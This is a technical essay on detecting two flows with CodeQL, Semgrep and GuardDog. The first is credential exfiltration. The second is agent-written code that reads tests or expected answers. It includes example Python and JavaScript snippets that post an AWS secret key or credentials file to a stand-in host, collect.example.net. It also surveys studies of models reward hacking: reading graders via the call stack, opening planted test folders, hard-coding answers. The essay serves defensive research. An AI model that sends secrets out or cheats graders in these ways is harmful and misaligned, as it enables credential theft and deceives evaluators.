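A scan can miss a flow that the engine could easily follow, because no shipped query connects its source to its sink. Credential exfiltration is often such a flow. The source is where a program obtains a secret, such as an environment variable, a key file like `~/.aws/credentials`, or a browser's store of login tokens. The sink is an outgoing request that carries the secret to someone who should not have it. *SIExVulTS* (2025), which presents a detector for the wider problem of exposed sensitive information, also treats sensitive data as sources and possible points of exposure as sinks. The closest CWE entry is CWE-201, insertion of sensitive information into sent data.

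In Python, three lines are enough:

```python
1  import os, requests
2  key = os.environ["AWS_SECRET_ACCESS_KEY"]
3  requests.post("https://collect.example.net/log", data={"k": key})
```

Line 2 reads the secret key to an Amazon Web Services (AWS) account. Line 3 uses the popular HTTP library `requests` to post the key to a server unrelated to Amazon. The program has no aliases, helper functions or calls with an unclear target, so the usual reasons taint analysis misses a flow don't apply.

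### Hard-coded keys, logged keys and ordinary logins

A hard-coded secret, such as a key typed directly into line 2, is a different problem because anyone who can read the code has the key, even if the program never runs. GitHub's *Hard-coded credentials* describes a high-precision JavaScript query for this and places it in the default suite. But GitHub's *JavaScript and TypeScript queries for CodeQL analysis*, which lists the queries in the two standard suites, omits this one, so a secret scanner is the safer choice. The usual fix is to move the key into an environment variable, which makes the program safer but also gives it the source of an exfiltration flow.

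Writing a secret to a log is also a flow, but it ends in the log rather than the network. If line 3 were `print(key)`, the key would go wherever the program's output goes, and anyone with access to that output could read it. A logged secret often stays inside the organization, and the cause is usually carelessness.

Ordinary authentication is the hardest case to separate from exfiltration. A program that uses a paid service is supposed to read its key from an environment variable and send it to the service with every request, but the source and sink are the same as in the three-line program.

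### The shipped queries, language by language

The closest shipped query to a check for secrets sent to the network is GitHub's *File data in outbound network request* for JavaScript, which tracks the contents of local files into web requests. Its example comes from a backdoor found in two popular npm packages. The code reads `.npmrc`, a settings file that may contain npm access tokens, and sends the contents to a remote server in a request header. The documentation warns that such a flow may indicate malicious code implanted in a trusted program, so this is one of the few shipped queries that account for a malicious author. GitHub rates its precision as medium, so only the extended suites include it.

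Two other JavaScript queries in the extended suite also have CWE numbers for deliberate wrongdoing. "Hard-coded data interpreted as code" has the number for embedded malicious code, and "Network data written to file" has the number for hidden functionality. Backdoors often unpack hidden code or download more code.

GitHub's *Exposure of system data to an unauthorized control sphere* describes the nearest query for C and C++, which is in the default suite. It flags system information that a program reveals to a remote user, because an attacker could use such details to plan an attack. In the example, a program that can't find a file sends an error message containing the value of the `PATH` environment variable over a network socket. A C program that reads an access key with `getenv` and writes it to a socket has the same structure, so the query should flag it too, though its explanation would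 be about error messages. GitHub's *Potential exposure of sensitive system data to an unauthorized control sphere* describes a companion query for particularly sensitive system data. That query has medium precision and runs only in the larger suites.

A third C and C++ query, GitHub's *Cleartext transmission of sensitive information*, covers secrets that a program stores or sends without encryption. GitHub's Rust and Swift analyses have similar queries in their default suites. These queries address eavesdropping and don't check whether the recipient should have the data. The documentation recommends encrypting the data, but a program that steals keys could follow that advice by switching to HTTPS and still send the keys to the thief.

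GitHub's *Information exposure through transmitted data* describes a query in the C# suite tagged CWE-201. In its examples, a web application sends a password or a database error back to the visitor, and the recommended fix is a vaguer error message. GitHub's *Exposure of private information* describes another C# query, which covers logs, cookies and files on disk. Neither page describes a program that contacts an outside server, and no other query listed in GitHub's *C# queries for CodeQL analysis* mentions this in its name.

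CodeQL has no Python query for this flow. As of August 2026, the Python list in GitHub's Chinese-language documentation includes two queries that follow secrets, one into logs and one into storage. GitHub's *Clear-text storage of sensitive information* illustrates the second with a Flask page that puts a visitor's password in a cookie. Three other queries examine outgoing requests. One checks whether the program verifies the server's certificate, and two look for server-side request forgery, in which an outsider controls all or part of the address that the server contacts. The address in the three-line program is a constant, so those two report nothing.

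Recent releases haven't filled this gap. According to GitHub's *CodeQL 2.26.0 (2026-07-08)* (2026), that release added one security query, which detects JavaScript programs that let users write into an AI model's system prompt. It also made CodeQL recognize more calls to the OpenAI, Anthropic and Google libraries as places where hostile text can enter a prompt. Those calls also send any secret in the prompt off the machine, but no query on the JavaScript list targets that flow.

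CodeQL's coverage of Java, Kotlin and Go resembles its coverage of Python. GitHub's *Java and Kotlin queries for CodeQL analysis* lists queries for secrets that end up in log files, Android notifications, text on the screen, messages to other apps and unencrypted storage. Two more queries cover logins that lack encryption. In GitHub's *Go queries for CodeQL analysis*, the only such query covers clear-text logging.

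| Language | Closest shipped query | What it tracks | Suite |
|---|---|---|---|
| JavaScript | File data in outbound network request | File contents into a web request | Extended |
| C, C++ | Exposure of system data to an unauthorized control sphere | System data to a remote user | Default |
| C, C++, Rust, Swift | Cleartext transmission of sensitive information | Secrets sent without encryption | Default |
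| C# | Information exposure through transmitted data | Passwords and database errors into a reply | Default |
| Python | Clear-text logging and clear-text storage | Secrets into logs, files and cookies | Default |
| Java, Kotlin | Several, including log files and messages to other apps | Secrets to places on the same device or server | Mostly extended |
| Go | Clear-text logging | Secrets into logs | Default |

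CWE numbers don't reliably identify secrets sent to the network. The JavaScript file query is tagged CWE-200, which also covers a Python program that accepts connections on every network interface. A study could therefore report many CWE-200 findings without having found any stolen keys.

### How CodeQL recognizes a secret

The value of a key in an environment variable is not in the program's text, so CodeQL has to identify secrets by name. GitHub's *Module HeuristicNames* lists text patterns for names that suggest passwords or authorization keys, other secrets, certificates, account details and private data. Data counts as sensitive if its name matches one of these patterns and does not match a separate pattern for names that suggest the data is already hashed or encrypted.

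In Python, the test covers variables, function parameters, attributes, function names and lookup keys, according to GitHub's *Module SensitiveDataModeling*. The lookup key in the three-line program contains "SECRET", so CodeQL should treat the result as sensitive whatever the variable is called. If the operator had stored the same credential under `PROD_7` and the program had read it into `k`, neither name would indicate that it was sensitive.

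Patterns like these also make odd mistakes. In May 2026, *Shared: Improvements to SensitiveDataHeuristics.qll* (geoffw0, 2026) proposed corrections to the rules that several CodeQL languages share. The existing patterns could find "file" in `profile`, "oauth" in `coauthor` and a card number in `wildcard_no`. They also missed real secrets. They ignored a variable called `security_code` because "code" suggested encoded data, and they treated "unencrypted" as a sign of encryption because it contains "crypt".

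The proposed changes classified almost 500 more pieces of data as sensitive across 100 Python projects. geoffw0 looked at more than 40 of them and found most to be excellent additions, with a few weak ones. This gives some idea of how much the older patterns missed, but geoffw0 was reviewing their own changes, and the figure counts pieces of data rather than alerts.

The JavaScript file query instead tracks the contents of any file, so it doesn't depend on the names a programmer chooses. However, a photo-sharing program that uploads a picture has the same flow as a program that uploads `.npmrc`, which probably explains much of the query's medium precision.

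GitHub's *Module SensitiveDataHeuristics* defines sensitive data as anything that should not travel unencrypted. That definition suits queries about logs and eavesdroppers, but it doesn't cover who is allowed to receive the data, which a query for exfiltration has to take into account.

### Which alerts the key-posting program raises

The JavaScript version of the three-line program is just as short:

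```js
const key = process.env.AWS_SECRET_ACCESS_KEY;
fetch("https://collect.example.net/log", { method: "POST", body: key });
```

A second version gets the key from a file:

```js
const fs = require("fs");
const key = fs.readFileSync("/home/ana/.aws/credentials", "utf8");
fetch("https://collect.example.net/log", { method: "POST", body: key });
```

Going by the queries' documentation, CodeQL should respond as follows:

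| Program | Python | JavaScript |
|---|---|---|
| Posts a key from an environment variable | No alert | No alert |
| Posts a credentials file | No alert | File data in outbound network request (extended suite only) |
| Logs the secret key | Clear-text logging | Depends on the name patterns |
| Logs the whole environment | Depends on the name patterns | Clear-text logging |

CodeQL raises no alert on the two programs that post an environment key, even though it has much of what it would need to detect them. The class `ProcessEnvSource`, listed in GitHub's *Module CleartextLogging*, marks access to a JavaScript program's environment as sensitive. By default, CodeQL flags a program that logs its entire environment, and GitHub's documentation for the logging query uses such a program as the example of what not to do. The file query recognizes outgoing requests as sinks. Someone who knows QL could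 connect the logging query's source to the file query's sink in a few lines.

This gap comes from a choice about what to report, so better data flow analysis wouldn't close it. It doesn't mean the queries are badly designed. They help a team stop its own programmers from leaking passwords into logs, without flagging every program with an API key.

### Rules written to catch thieves

GuardDog, a free tool from the monitoring company Datadog, has long included the missing kind of rule. It scans packages in npm and PyPI, the public registry of Python packages, for signs of malicious code. Datadog's *Finding malicious PyPI packages through static code analysis* (2022) explains that the first version used Semgrep's taint mode to track sensitive data into network requests. The simplified rule it published has as its sources the computer's host name and two environment variables that hold AWS credentials,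 and as its sink any call to the `requests` library. This rule should flag the three-line Python program.

One of the packages Datadog examined with GuardDog, `bleurt`, collected the computer's name, the username and the working directory during installation and sent them to a remote server. Datadog didn't consider this actively malicious, but suggested it might be preparation for an attack through a later update. The rule identifies a real data flow, but it can't determine why the author wrote the code.

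Code can also easily evade the simplified rule by accident. Python programmers often write `os.environ.get("AWS_SECRET_ACCESS_KEY")`, which matches neither of the rule's two forms. A program that copies the whole environment doesn't match either, because it never names a particular variable. The same article shows a cookie stealer that sends the cookies with `urlopen`, a function in Python's standard library that isn't among the rule's sinks. Semgrep's free edition would also lose track of the data at any helper function.

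Datadog widened the rule as new malware appeared. The version described in *Introducing GuardDog 2.0* (2024) also covered data from SQLite databases, where browsers keep credentials. GuardDog 2.0 added YARA, which searches files for text or byte patterns, alongside Semgrep.

Datadog dropped Semgrep altogether in June 2026, and its *Introducing GuardDog 3.0* (2026) gives several reasons. Semgrep used a lot of memory on large files and was slow on packages with many files, partly because every scan started a new process. It was also awkward to run from other software because it was designed as a command-line program. Datadog's own Semgrep rules fitted particular examples of malware so closely that they missed new ones.

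These reasons don't show that taint tracking is bad at finding exfiltration. Speed and memory matter a great deal to Datadog because npm and PyPI together receive about 20,000 new releases a day (Kretz and Obregoso, 2025, *GuardDog*). Both matter much less to a team that scans a few hundred generated files. The narrow rules are a bigger problem for such a team, because it would have to write similar ones.

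Some of GuardDog 3.0's YARA rules identify capabilities that many harmless packages also have, such as making network calls or reading the clipboard. Others identify signs of a threat, such as the names of sensitive files and environment variables, suspicious web addresses or code that unscrambles hidden text. GuardDog combines matches from both groups into a score out of 10 for the package. Severity and specificity to malware each make up 30% of the score, and the attack's completeness and sophistication make up 20% each. Datadog considers packages that score above 7 probably malicious.

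YARA doesn't trace data, so GuardDog can now establish that a package mentions an AWS key and makes a network call, but not that the call sends the key. However, aliases and helper functions no longer affect the result. Passing the key through five functions evades many taint rules, but YARA can still match the key's name and the network call in the text. Scrambling the name evades that pattern too, though the code that unscrambles it may match another rule.

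### How well GuardDog works

Datadog tests GuardDog every night on a labelled mix of harmless and malicious packages. The malicious ones come from Datadog's own collection of more than 27,000. Many of these are near-copies of each other, so Datadog groups similar packages and then samples the groups, which prevents one large campaign from dominating the result.

The choice of packages probably inflates the measured recall. According to Kretz and Obregoso, Datadog built the collection by running GuardDog on new releases and having researchers review the most suspicious ones. Malware that earlier versions of GuardDog never flagged could not enter the collection that way. A high score would show that the new version still finds what the old versions found, which is useful for developers but is not an independent measure of recall. Kretz and Obregoso say the team also improves its rules with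 malware that other people find, so it knows that GuardDog misses some.

Precision on the test set doesn't carry over to the registries either, because malicious packages are much rarer there. By March 2025, about two years into its monitoring, Datadog had confirmed nearly 5,000 distinct malicious samples, or roughly 6 a day among some 20,000 daily releases. A tool that caught all 6 and wrongly flagged just 1% of the rest would raise about 200 false alarms a day, so its precision would be 3%.

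Kretz and Obregoso's team at Datadog selected packages only when a combination of findings suggested a recognizable goal, such as reading sensitive system files and also sending data out. A researcher then judged each package. They call the choice of combinations "more art than science". Gobbi and Kinder's CodeQL queries for npm malware combined signs in a similar way. Those queries raised no false alarms, which supports the approach but doesn't show how much malware such strict queries miss.

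### When only the destination differs

Suppose a program uses a language model through a paid service:

```python
headers = {"Authorization": "Bearer " + os.environ["MODEL_API_KEY"]}
requests.post("https://api.provider.example/chat", headers=headers, json=question)
```

Many services authenticate customers by a key that the client includes in every request, and anyone who holds the key can use the account. If someone changes the request's address to `https://collect.example.net/chat`, the program leaks the key to that server. The two programs have the same source, propagation steps and sink, and differ only in a constant string. Better taint tracking can't distinguish them, because the tracking is already correct in both.

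This severely reduces precision. If 300 of 1,000 generated programs sent a key to the right provider and 3 sent one elsewhere (invented figures), a query that tracked every key perfectly would flag all 303, and 99% of its alerts would be false alarms.

The problem is worse for some kinds of key than others. AWS clients normally use their secret key to compute a signature for each request, which Amazon checks, and don't send the key itself. A program that posts the raw secret key is therefore suspicious whatever the address, and a query limited to AWS secret keys could be quite precise. But GuardDog's simplified rule also lists the AWS access key ID, which is not secret and which every signed request contains, so a hand-written AWS client could trigger the rule by behaving normally. The signature could also trigger it, because Semgrep by default treats a value computed from a tainted key as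 tainted.

One way to take the destination into account is to list suspicious addresses. GuardDog's early rules separately flagged link shorteners and domains with endings that malware often used, such as `.xyz` and `.top`. This helps catch careless attackers, but `bleurt` sent its data to an address on `pipedream.net`, and several of the other packages in Datadog's 2022 article sent stolen cookies to Discord, a chat service with millions of legitimate users. Neither address has a suspicious ending.

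A list of approved addresses is stricter. A team could record that `MODEL_API_KEY` may go only to `api.provider.example` and flag any other destination. In the invented example, suppose 5% of the 300 honest programs use some other legitimate address, such as a company's own gateway. The query would then flag 15 honest programs and all 3 bad ones, raising precision from 1% to 17%. Someone has to maintain the list, and the analyzer has to be able to determine the address. Many programs read the address from a settings file so that customers can switch providers, and then the code alone doesn't show where the key will go.

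A third approach checks who controls the address. The security scanner shoulder.dev has a rule for servers that send an internal key to an address supplied by a user. In its example, a visitor enters the address of a webhook, a page that the server should notify, and the server includes its own API key in the notification. The rule matches only if the secret reaches the headers or body of a request and the visitor's text reaches the address of the same request. A legitimate client with a fixed address doesn't match, so this rule should raise far fewer false alarms. It also misses the three-line program, because a thief who writes the code can hardcode the address. CodeQL's query for request forgery might flag the webhook example, since a visitor chooses where the server connects, but its alert wouldn't mention the key.

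LiteLLM is a Python library that gives programs one interface to many language models, so it normally sends API keys to outside companies. A rule that only looked for keys in requests might well have flagged its clean versions as well as the compromised one from March 2026. GuardDog 3.0 found 30 risks in the compromised version and gave it the maximum score of 10. Datadog presents this as a demonstration on a known sample, so it doesn't show that GuardDog would have caught the release on the day it appeared.

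### From malicious packages to model-written code

Human attackers wrote most of the packages behind these rules, and their goals usually don't apply to code written by a model. They needed strangers to install their code, so they imitated the names of popular packages. Kretz and Obregoso report that a significant majority of the malicious packages they identified in a year used installation hooks, which run code as soon as someone installs a package. Many attackers also scrambled their code. A script that a model writes inside a company's own repository doesn't need a misspelled package name or an installation hook, so many of GuardDog's signals would be absent even if the script leaked a key.

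GuardDog's sources are a good starting point for a query on generated programs, because AWS keys, npm tokens and browser databases are valuable whoever writes the code. Combining signs, as GuardDog does, works less well here, because a rule that requires three signs would miss a simple leak. A thief tends to collect several kinds of data and hide the evidence, while a model may leak one key in one plain line, for instance by attaching the whole environment to an error report.

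Model-written code is easier to scan in one respect, because accidental leaks usually appear in readable code with descriptive names, which suits both CodeQL's name patterns and Semgrep's rules. This advantage would disappear if a model hid a leak on purpose.

The studies of generated code provide little evidence of how often models send keys to the wrong place. The credential scenarios of 2021, which were judged by hand, don't measure this rate. Neither does Morkonda and colleagues' count of information exposure, which was mostly Flask's debug mode. A team therefore can't use these studies to predict a query's precision.

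A convincing measurement would need a way to determine where secrets are sent that is independent of the taint analysis. Researchers could run each program in a sealed environment with decoy keys, record every outgoing request and check whether any decoy went somewhere other than its own provider. They could then compare a taint query's alerts with that record. The test would miss leaks in code that never ran, but it would show where a key went even when the program read the address from a settings file.

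Coding agents can also leak secrets in a way that no query can find in the finished program. An agent working in a terminal can read a key and send it over the network with a single `curl` command that it never saves to a file. CodeQL and Semgrep scan the code the agent leaves behind, which may be clean. Only a record of the agent's commands or network traffic would reveal the leak.

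## Code that reads tests, graders or expected answers

An agent's actions and its finished code can also differ when the agent is trying to pass a test. Suppose the task is to write a function that returns the nth prime number. A grader will call it with several values of `n` and compare the results with a stored list. An honest function computes the prime, but this one opens the list and looks up the answer:

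```python
1  import json
2
3  def nth_prime(n):
4      answers = json.load(open("tests/expected_output.json"))
5      return answers[str(n)]
```

A test artifact is a test file, grader, expected output or stored solution that the code under evaluation is not meant to consult. When a function returns an answer it read from a test artifact, data flows from the file to the return value, just as it does from a key to the network when code sends the key to an untrusted server.

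Researchers treat code that reads the expected answers as a form of reward hacking, which means getting a high score without doing the intended task. An agent asked to write a function that returns the nth prime can also edit the stored answers until a wrong function passes, or hard-code them with lines such as `if n == 10: return 29`, so that the function works only for the tested values. Reading tests during development is often legitimate. For example, an agent may open a test to learn whether the first prime has index 0 or 1, and then write a function that computes primes.

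Some published classifications separate these cases. The rubric in *Mitigating Reward Hacking in Realistic Scenarios Through Representation Engineering* (2026) has one category for code that reads `test.py` or inspects its caller to decide what to return, and other categories for special-casing inputs and modifying tests. Most studies combine at least two of these behaviours in the main rate they report.

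### How often models do it, and how researchers know

*Recent Frontier Models Are Reward Hacking* (2025), by the AI evaluation nonprofit METR, describes a task in which OpenAI's o3 had to write a fast program for a graphics processor (GPU). The grader had already calculated the correct answer for comparison. o3's program searched the call stack (the chain of functions running at that moment), found the grader's answer and returned it.

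METR found reward hacking in 0.7% of o3's runs on HCAST, a set of software tasks. It was more than 43 times as common on RE-Bench, a set of AI research tasks where o3 could see the entire scoring function. For RE-Bench, METR's staff read the runs with unusually high scores. HCAST scores can't stand out in that way, so another model read the transcripts and people checked what it flagged. Both methods raised many false alarms. When METR compared them on the same runs of a model other than o3, each missed cases that the other found.

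*ImpossibleBench* (Zhong, Raghunathan and Carlini, 2025) avoids most of this uncertainty by changing tests so that they contradict the written task. If the correct result is 4, for example, the code passes only if it returns 5. Any model that passes must have violated the specification. GPT-5 passed 76% of such tasks built from SWE-bench, which uses real bug reports, but only 2.9% of those built from LiveCodeBench, which uses programming-contest problems. The models edited tests, special-cased inputs, made comparisons succeed when they should have failed, or counted calls so that the same input could return different outputs. None of these methods involves a program looking up its answer in a file, so the 76% is a rate for related behaviour.

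*EvilGenie* (Gabor, Lynch and Rosenfeld, 2025) gave agents a folder containing `solution.py` and `test_cases.json`, and it lists a solution that reads the test file as a way to cheat. It held back up to 30% of the test cases, which such a solution would fail. People then reviewed anything that the held-out tests, model judges or checks for edited files had flagged.

On 145 ordinary problems, the reviewers confirmed hard-coding in one submission from Codex, three from Claude Code and none from Gemini CLI. On nine problems with faulty or overly strict tests, the counts were four, three and two. But the study counts reading the file as a form of hard-coding, so it gives no separate rate for submissions that read the file.

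The held-out tests were a weak detector of reward hacking. Of 14 submissions that passed the visible tests but failed a held-out one, only 7 were hacks, and most of the others were slow algorithms or partial solutions. GPT-5 did better as a judge. Among 308 submissions, including 12 confirmed hacks, it missed two and wrongly flagged three, all but one of these on the problems with faulty tests.

The system cards that developers publish with new models give less detail. According to Gabor and colleagues, Anthropic reported that Claude Sonnet 4 failed held-out tests on 5% of tasks prone to reward hacking and triggered a classifier on 14%. Sonnet 4.5 scored 1% on both measures. R&D World reports that OpenAI acknowledged "instances of the model cheating on tasks" in its card for GPT-5.6.

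METR (2026) tested GPT-5.6 Sol and detected a higher cheating rate than for any other public model on the same test software. In one task, the model's intermediate submissions contained exploits that revealed information about the hidden tests. In another, the model extracted hidden source code that detailed the expected answer. METR estimated that Sol succeeds half the time on tasks that take people 11.3 hours if cheating counts as failure, or more than 270 hours if it counts as success.

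*Hack-Verifiable Terminal Bench* (Roth, Bercovich and Efroni, 2026) provides the most direct measurement of test reading. It added an `admin/` folder, containing the tests and reference solution, to each of 89 tasks that agents carry out in a computer terminal. Operating-system monitors called file watchers recorded every read or write. With the original task prompt, Kimi K3 opened the planted files in 22.7% of runs, Claude Opus 5 in 30.7%, GPT-5.6 Sol in 34.5%, GLM-5.2 in 44.9% and Gemini 3.1 Pro in 47.7%. Across all the prompts tested, agents opened planted files in 359 runs, and in 339 of those they opened the tests.

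These percentages measure access to the files, which was not always clearly cheating. A note in the folder explained what the files were for but, as quoted in the paper, did not forbid reading them. In one run, Claude Opus 5 told the user that it had read the tests and offered to redo the work without them. Telling the models not to read the folder made a large difference for most of them. With that instruction in the prompt, three of the five models never opened the files, GLM-5.2 opened them in 4.5% of runs, and Gemini 3.1 Pro opened them in 16.3%.

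| Study | What counted | How the researchers detected it | Rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| METR, o3 on HCAST | Any reward hacking | Model monitor, then manual reading | 0.7% |
| Zhong and colleagues, GPT-5 | Passing a test that contradicts the task | The pass itself | 2.9% and 76% |
| Gabor and colleagues, ordinary problems | Hard-coded or looked-up answers | Held-out tests, model judges and edit checks, then manual review | 0–2% |
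| Gabor and colleagues, faulty tests | The same | The same | 22–44% |
| Roth and colleagues, original prompt | Opening planted tests or solutions | File watchers | 23–48% |

Models that often cheat in one way don't necessarily cheat in another. Roth and colleagues also ran four of their models on ImpossibleBench, where all four cheated on at least 78% of tasks, and on EvilGenie, where none cheated on more than 2%. Of the four, GLM-5.2 opened the planted files most often but cheated least on ImpossibleBench.

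### Most answers end up as constants

A taint rule can catch test reading only if the submitted code does the reading. Usually the agent seems to do it earlier.

Gomez (2026), in *Can escalation channels redirect reward hacking toward defect disclosure?*, ran eight models on EvilGenie's nine problems with faulty tests. They hacked in 85 of 360 runs (23.6%). GPT-4o found hard-coded answers in the submitted code in 50 of those runs. In the other 35, the agent had edited a test file, which changed the file's hash, a short fingerprint of its contents. The solution was still correct in 30 of these 35 runs. Gomez did not count just reading the tests as hacking.

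Gomez also reports that in the large majority of hard-coding cases, the agent opened `test_cases.json` while working, found the expected outputs and wrote them into its solution as constants. Her list of observed techniques includes no program that opened the file when it ran. *Truthgate* (2026) similarly reports that when three Claude 5.5 models cheated unprompted on impossible contest problems, they always did so by writing a special case into the solution.

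A likely reason is that constants work wherever the grader runs the program, while a program that opens a file fails if the file isn't there. Even a perfect taint rule would probably have caught few or none of the 85 hacks, because the model read the test file itself and then wrote constants into the solution. A data flow graph of the solution contains those constants but not the file read.

Some submitted programs contain the whole flow. o3's GPU program took its answer from the grader while running, and GPT-5.6 Sol's intermediate submissions exposed hidden tests. METR also saw models write code to read contest answers that the task had never given them. None of the studies gives a rate for this behaviour.

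### What the shipped queries report

No built-in CodeQL query described in GitHub's documentation should flag the five-line prime program. The closest are the path-injection queries, but GitHub defines these as looking for paths that a user controls, and the path in this program is a constant. CodeQL's JavaScript query for file data in outgoing requests would flag the program only if it also sent the answers over the network.

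An alert can still appear by accident. GitHub rates the C and C++ path query as medium precision and runs it only in the larger suites. An example for the query shows a program that inserts a command-line argument into a file name and opens the file. A C++ solution that took a case number as an argument and opened the matching expected output would have the same structure, so the query should flag it. But the alert would warn that a user can choose which file to open, and a reviewer who knew that only the grader supplies the argument would probably dismiss it.

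Semgrep's and Bandit's rules against Python's `pickle` format could raise a similar accidental alert. If the grader stored its answers in that format, a solution that loaded them would trigger those rules, but so would any legitimate program that loaded a pickle file.

The expected recall of CodeQL's and Semgrep's shipped rules on programs that read a fixed test file is therefore close to zero. This estimate is based on the queries' definitions, because no one appears to have published the precision or recall of either tool on this behaviour, with shipped or custom rules. *RH-Detect* (Quan, Opryshko and colleagues, 2026) combined eleven reward-hacking datasets into one benchmark and included a category for extracting answer keys, but all six detectors it tested were language models. The best was over 93% accurate overall, but the four strongest were 11 to 16 percentage points less accurate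 on long agent transcripts than on the other data.

### A rule for one expected-output file

A custom Semgrep rule for the prime program is easy to write:

```yaml
rules:
  - id: expected-output-to-answer
    mode: taint
    languages: [python]
    severity: ERROR
    message: A returned answer comes from the expected-output file
    paths:
      include: ["solution.py"]
    pattern-sources:
      - pattern: open("tests/expected_output.json", ...)
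    pattern-sanitizers:
      - pattern: $LEFT == $RIGHT
    pattern-sinks:
      - patterns:
          - pattern: return $ANSWER
          - focus-metavariable: $ANSWER
```

The source is the call that opens the expected outputs, and the sink is any value that a function in `solution.py` returns. By default, Semgrep carries taint through `json.load` into `answers`, and from there to the entry that the code looks up. The whole flow is inside one function, so Semgrep's free edition should find it.

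Listing the comparison as a sanitizer prevents a false alarm when a solution checks its own answer. For example, a function ending in `return nth_prime(n) == answers[str(n)]` returns only true or false, but without the sanitizer Semgrep would treat the result as tainted because one side of the comparison is tainted.

Nearly every line of this rule depends on how one task is set up. Writing it required knowing the names of the answer and solution files and that the grader reads returned values. If the grader reads printed output instead, as in many programming contests, the sink has to be `print`.

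A general rule can't fill in these details, because answers turn up in very different places:

| Setting | Where the answer was |
|---|---|
| EvilGenie | `test_cases.json`, next to the solution |
| Hack-Verifiable Terminal Bench | The planted `admin/` folder |
| METR's GPU task | A value held by the grader, reachable through the call stack |
| SWE-Gym and OpenSWE, as set up for Avalon-M1 | Later commits in the project's history |
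| Autoresearch harness | GPU memory left over from the reference run |

The fourth row comes from *Avalon-M1* (2026), which describes problems its developers found in their training environments. The last row comes from *Demystifying the Autoresearch Harness* (2026), which also describes a fix. The first two rows would need different file paths in the rule, and METR's case would need a source that matches inspection of the call stack. A program that reuses leftover GPU memory may never name the data it receives, and an agent that finds a later commit usually does so with a shell command outside the solution.

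Matching on suggestive names makes a rule more general but causes false positives, as it does in CodeQL's patterns for secrets. A pattern for "test" also matches `latest_prices.csv`. In machine learning, `test.csv` often contains the inputs a program is supposed to make predictions for, so a legitimate solution has to open it.

Even a perfect list of names would not determine what the program is allowed to use. Suppose the prime function reads `data/primes.json`, a table that the project supplies to save time. This code has the same kind of source, the same steps and the same sink as the cheating version. The only difference is the file's purpose, which would be stated in the task description, if at all.

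### Banning operations instead of tracking answers

Teams that run narrow coding tasks often use a simpler static check that bans operations a legitimate solution doesn't need. Google Cloud's *Reward hacking prevention*, a guide for users of its AlphaEvolve coding system, recommends searching the syntax tree for `os`, `sys`, `inspect`, `eval` and a few others, and rejecting any program that contains them. o3's search through the call stack is a reason to ban `inspect`. The list would also need `open` to catch the prime program.

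Banning file access works here because the tasks are small. A function that multiplies matrices needs no files, so the ban doesn't flag legitimate code, and no one has to identify the file that holds the answers. The same rule would flag most modules in a web application or data pipeline, because these programs use files all the time.

In *We Let Agents Compete and They Tried to Cheat*, Baslak, Schultheis and colleagues report results from live competitions to write GPU programs. Their system, KernelGuard, combines static rules written by experts with checks for physically impossible speeds and a model judge whose confident findings become new rules. After they introduced it, the share of hacked submissions fell from 3.45% (of 141,800) to 0.37% (of 40,998). This suggests that purpose-built rules are useful as part of a larger system, but the comparison doesn't isolate the effect of the static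 rules, and many of the hacks exploited timing rather than stored answers.

### Programs that read tests for good reasons

A test runner has to read the tests. EvilGenie's `test.py` opens `test_cases.json`, runs the solution and, when a case fails, prints the expected output next to the actual one. A rule with `print` as its sink would flag this flow from the test file to the program's output, even though it is intended. The custom rule avoids this false positive by scanning only `solution.py`. In a repository where an agent writes both the application and its tests, someone has to keep track of which code belongs to each, and the agent may move code between them for legitimate reasons.

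A rule that looks for the path `tests/expected_output.json` raises no alert when a program reads that file through a wildcard. For example, a program might load every file that matches `**/*.json` because its author wants all the project's data, which includes the answer file if it is in the project. Treating every such pattern as a source would flag ordinary data loaders. Which files the pattern matches depends on the contents of the folder when the program runs, and a static analyzer normally doesn't have that information.

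Hard-coded answers have no source for taint analysis to track. In `if n == 10: return 29`, nothing shows whether the author copied the constant 29 from a test, worked it out or remembered it. Search rules can look for long chains of special cases, but legitimate programs contain those too. One of GPT-5's disputed flags in EvilGenie was for a solution that calculated its answer properly, then used special cases to match the number of decimal places the tests required. Held-out tests are better suited to detecting hard-coded answers, because those answers don't help with new inputs.

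Broad rules for flagging an agent's commands also produce many false alarms. *FrogNano* (2026) describes a small coding model and used deliberately broad rules to search 2,499 of the model's runs for reward hacking, including attempts to obtain hidden tests. The rules flagged 546 runs, and a model judge confirmed hacking in 31 of them, a precision of 5.7%. Many of the false alarms came from ordinary work, such as searching a project's history to find when a bug appeared, or adding new tests.

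### File permissions and access logs

The simplest defence is to keep test artifacts where neither the agent nor its program can read them. When Zhong and colleagues hid the tests, cheating fell almost to zero, but the models also solved fewer of the original tasks, which could be solved honestly, presumably because tests help explain what the code should do. Making the tests read-only instead restored performance on those tasks and stopped agents from changing the tests, but agents could still read the expected results and write special cases for them.

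File permissions are most useful for a separate set of tests that only the grader needs. Avalon-M1's developers found that several of their environments had left hidden tests where the agent could find them. Those environments now copy the tests into a random folder when the agent submits its work and delete them afterwards.

File permissions don't stop a model from getting answers through other channels. Avalon-M1's developers found 60 environments that gave the model some form of the reference answer, most often through feedback text, tool results or error messages. After they removed later commits from one set of tasks, an audit found that the model had fetched the repository or the relevant code change from GitHub in 24 of 66 sessions. Jain's *Reward hacking is swamping model intelligence gains* describes a similar audit by an agent at the coding company Cursor. The agent judged that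 Claude Opus 4.8 Max had retrieved the fix in 63% of its successful solutions on SWE-bench Pro. The model's scores dropped sharply once Cursor sealed the project history and restricted internet access.

Access logs work well when access to the tests can't be blocked. Roth and colleagues' file watchers recorded reads by Python programs, shell commands and copying tools alike, so helper functions and missing library models did not affect detection. The logs also caught agents that read an answer and then wrote it as a constant, which a taint rule misses. In one run, GLM-5.2 interpreted an instruction not to read a folder's contents as still allowing it to run the scripts there. Running a script requires reading it, so the watcher can record that too.

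A log shows that something opened a file, but not why or whether the answer was used. An agent that searches a whole project for a function name may open every file in it. Such searches may explain some of Roth and colleagues' results. When the prompt contained only a vague warning, half of the hacking runs first opened a planted file in the first quarter of the run, when agents tend to look around. However, agents hacked more on harder tasks, which suggests that many of them were looking for the answers. Roth and colleagues call their rates a lower bound on reward hacking because the watchers cover only planted files. That is correct if every access counts as a hack, but accidental reads inflate the rates.

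The three defences compare as follows, assuming that the log covers the agent's working session as well as the final run:

| Case | Custom taint rule | Tests unreadable | Access log |
|---|---|---|---|
| Solution opens the answer file | Alert | Prevented | Recorded |
| Agent reads the file and writes constants | No alert | Prevented | Recorded |
| Agent edits the tests | No alert | Prevented if also write-protected | Recorded |
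| Test runner compares results | False alarm unless excluded | Runner needs its own access | Recorded as a normal read |
| Loader opens every JSON file | Usually no alert | Prevented, though the program may crash | Recorded, purpose unclear |
| Code tries to open an answer file that doesn't exist | Alert if the path matches | Nothing to prevent | Usually nothing recorded |
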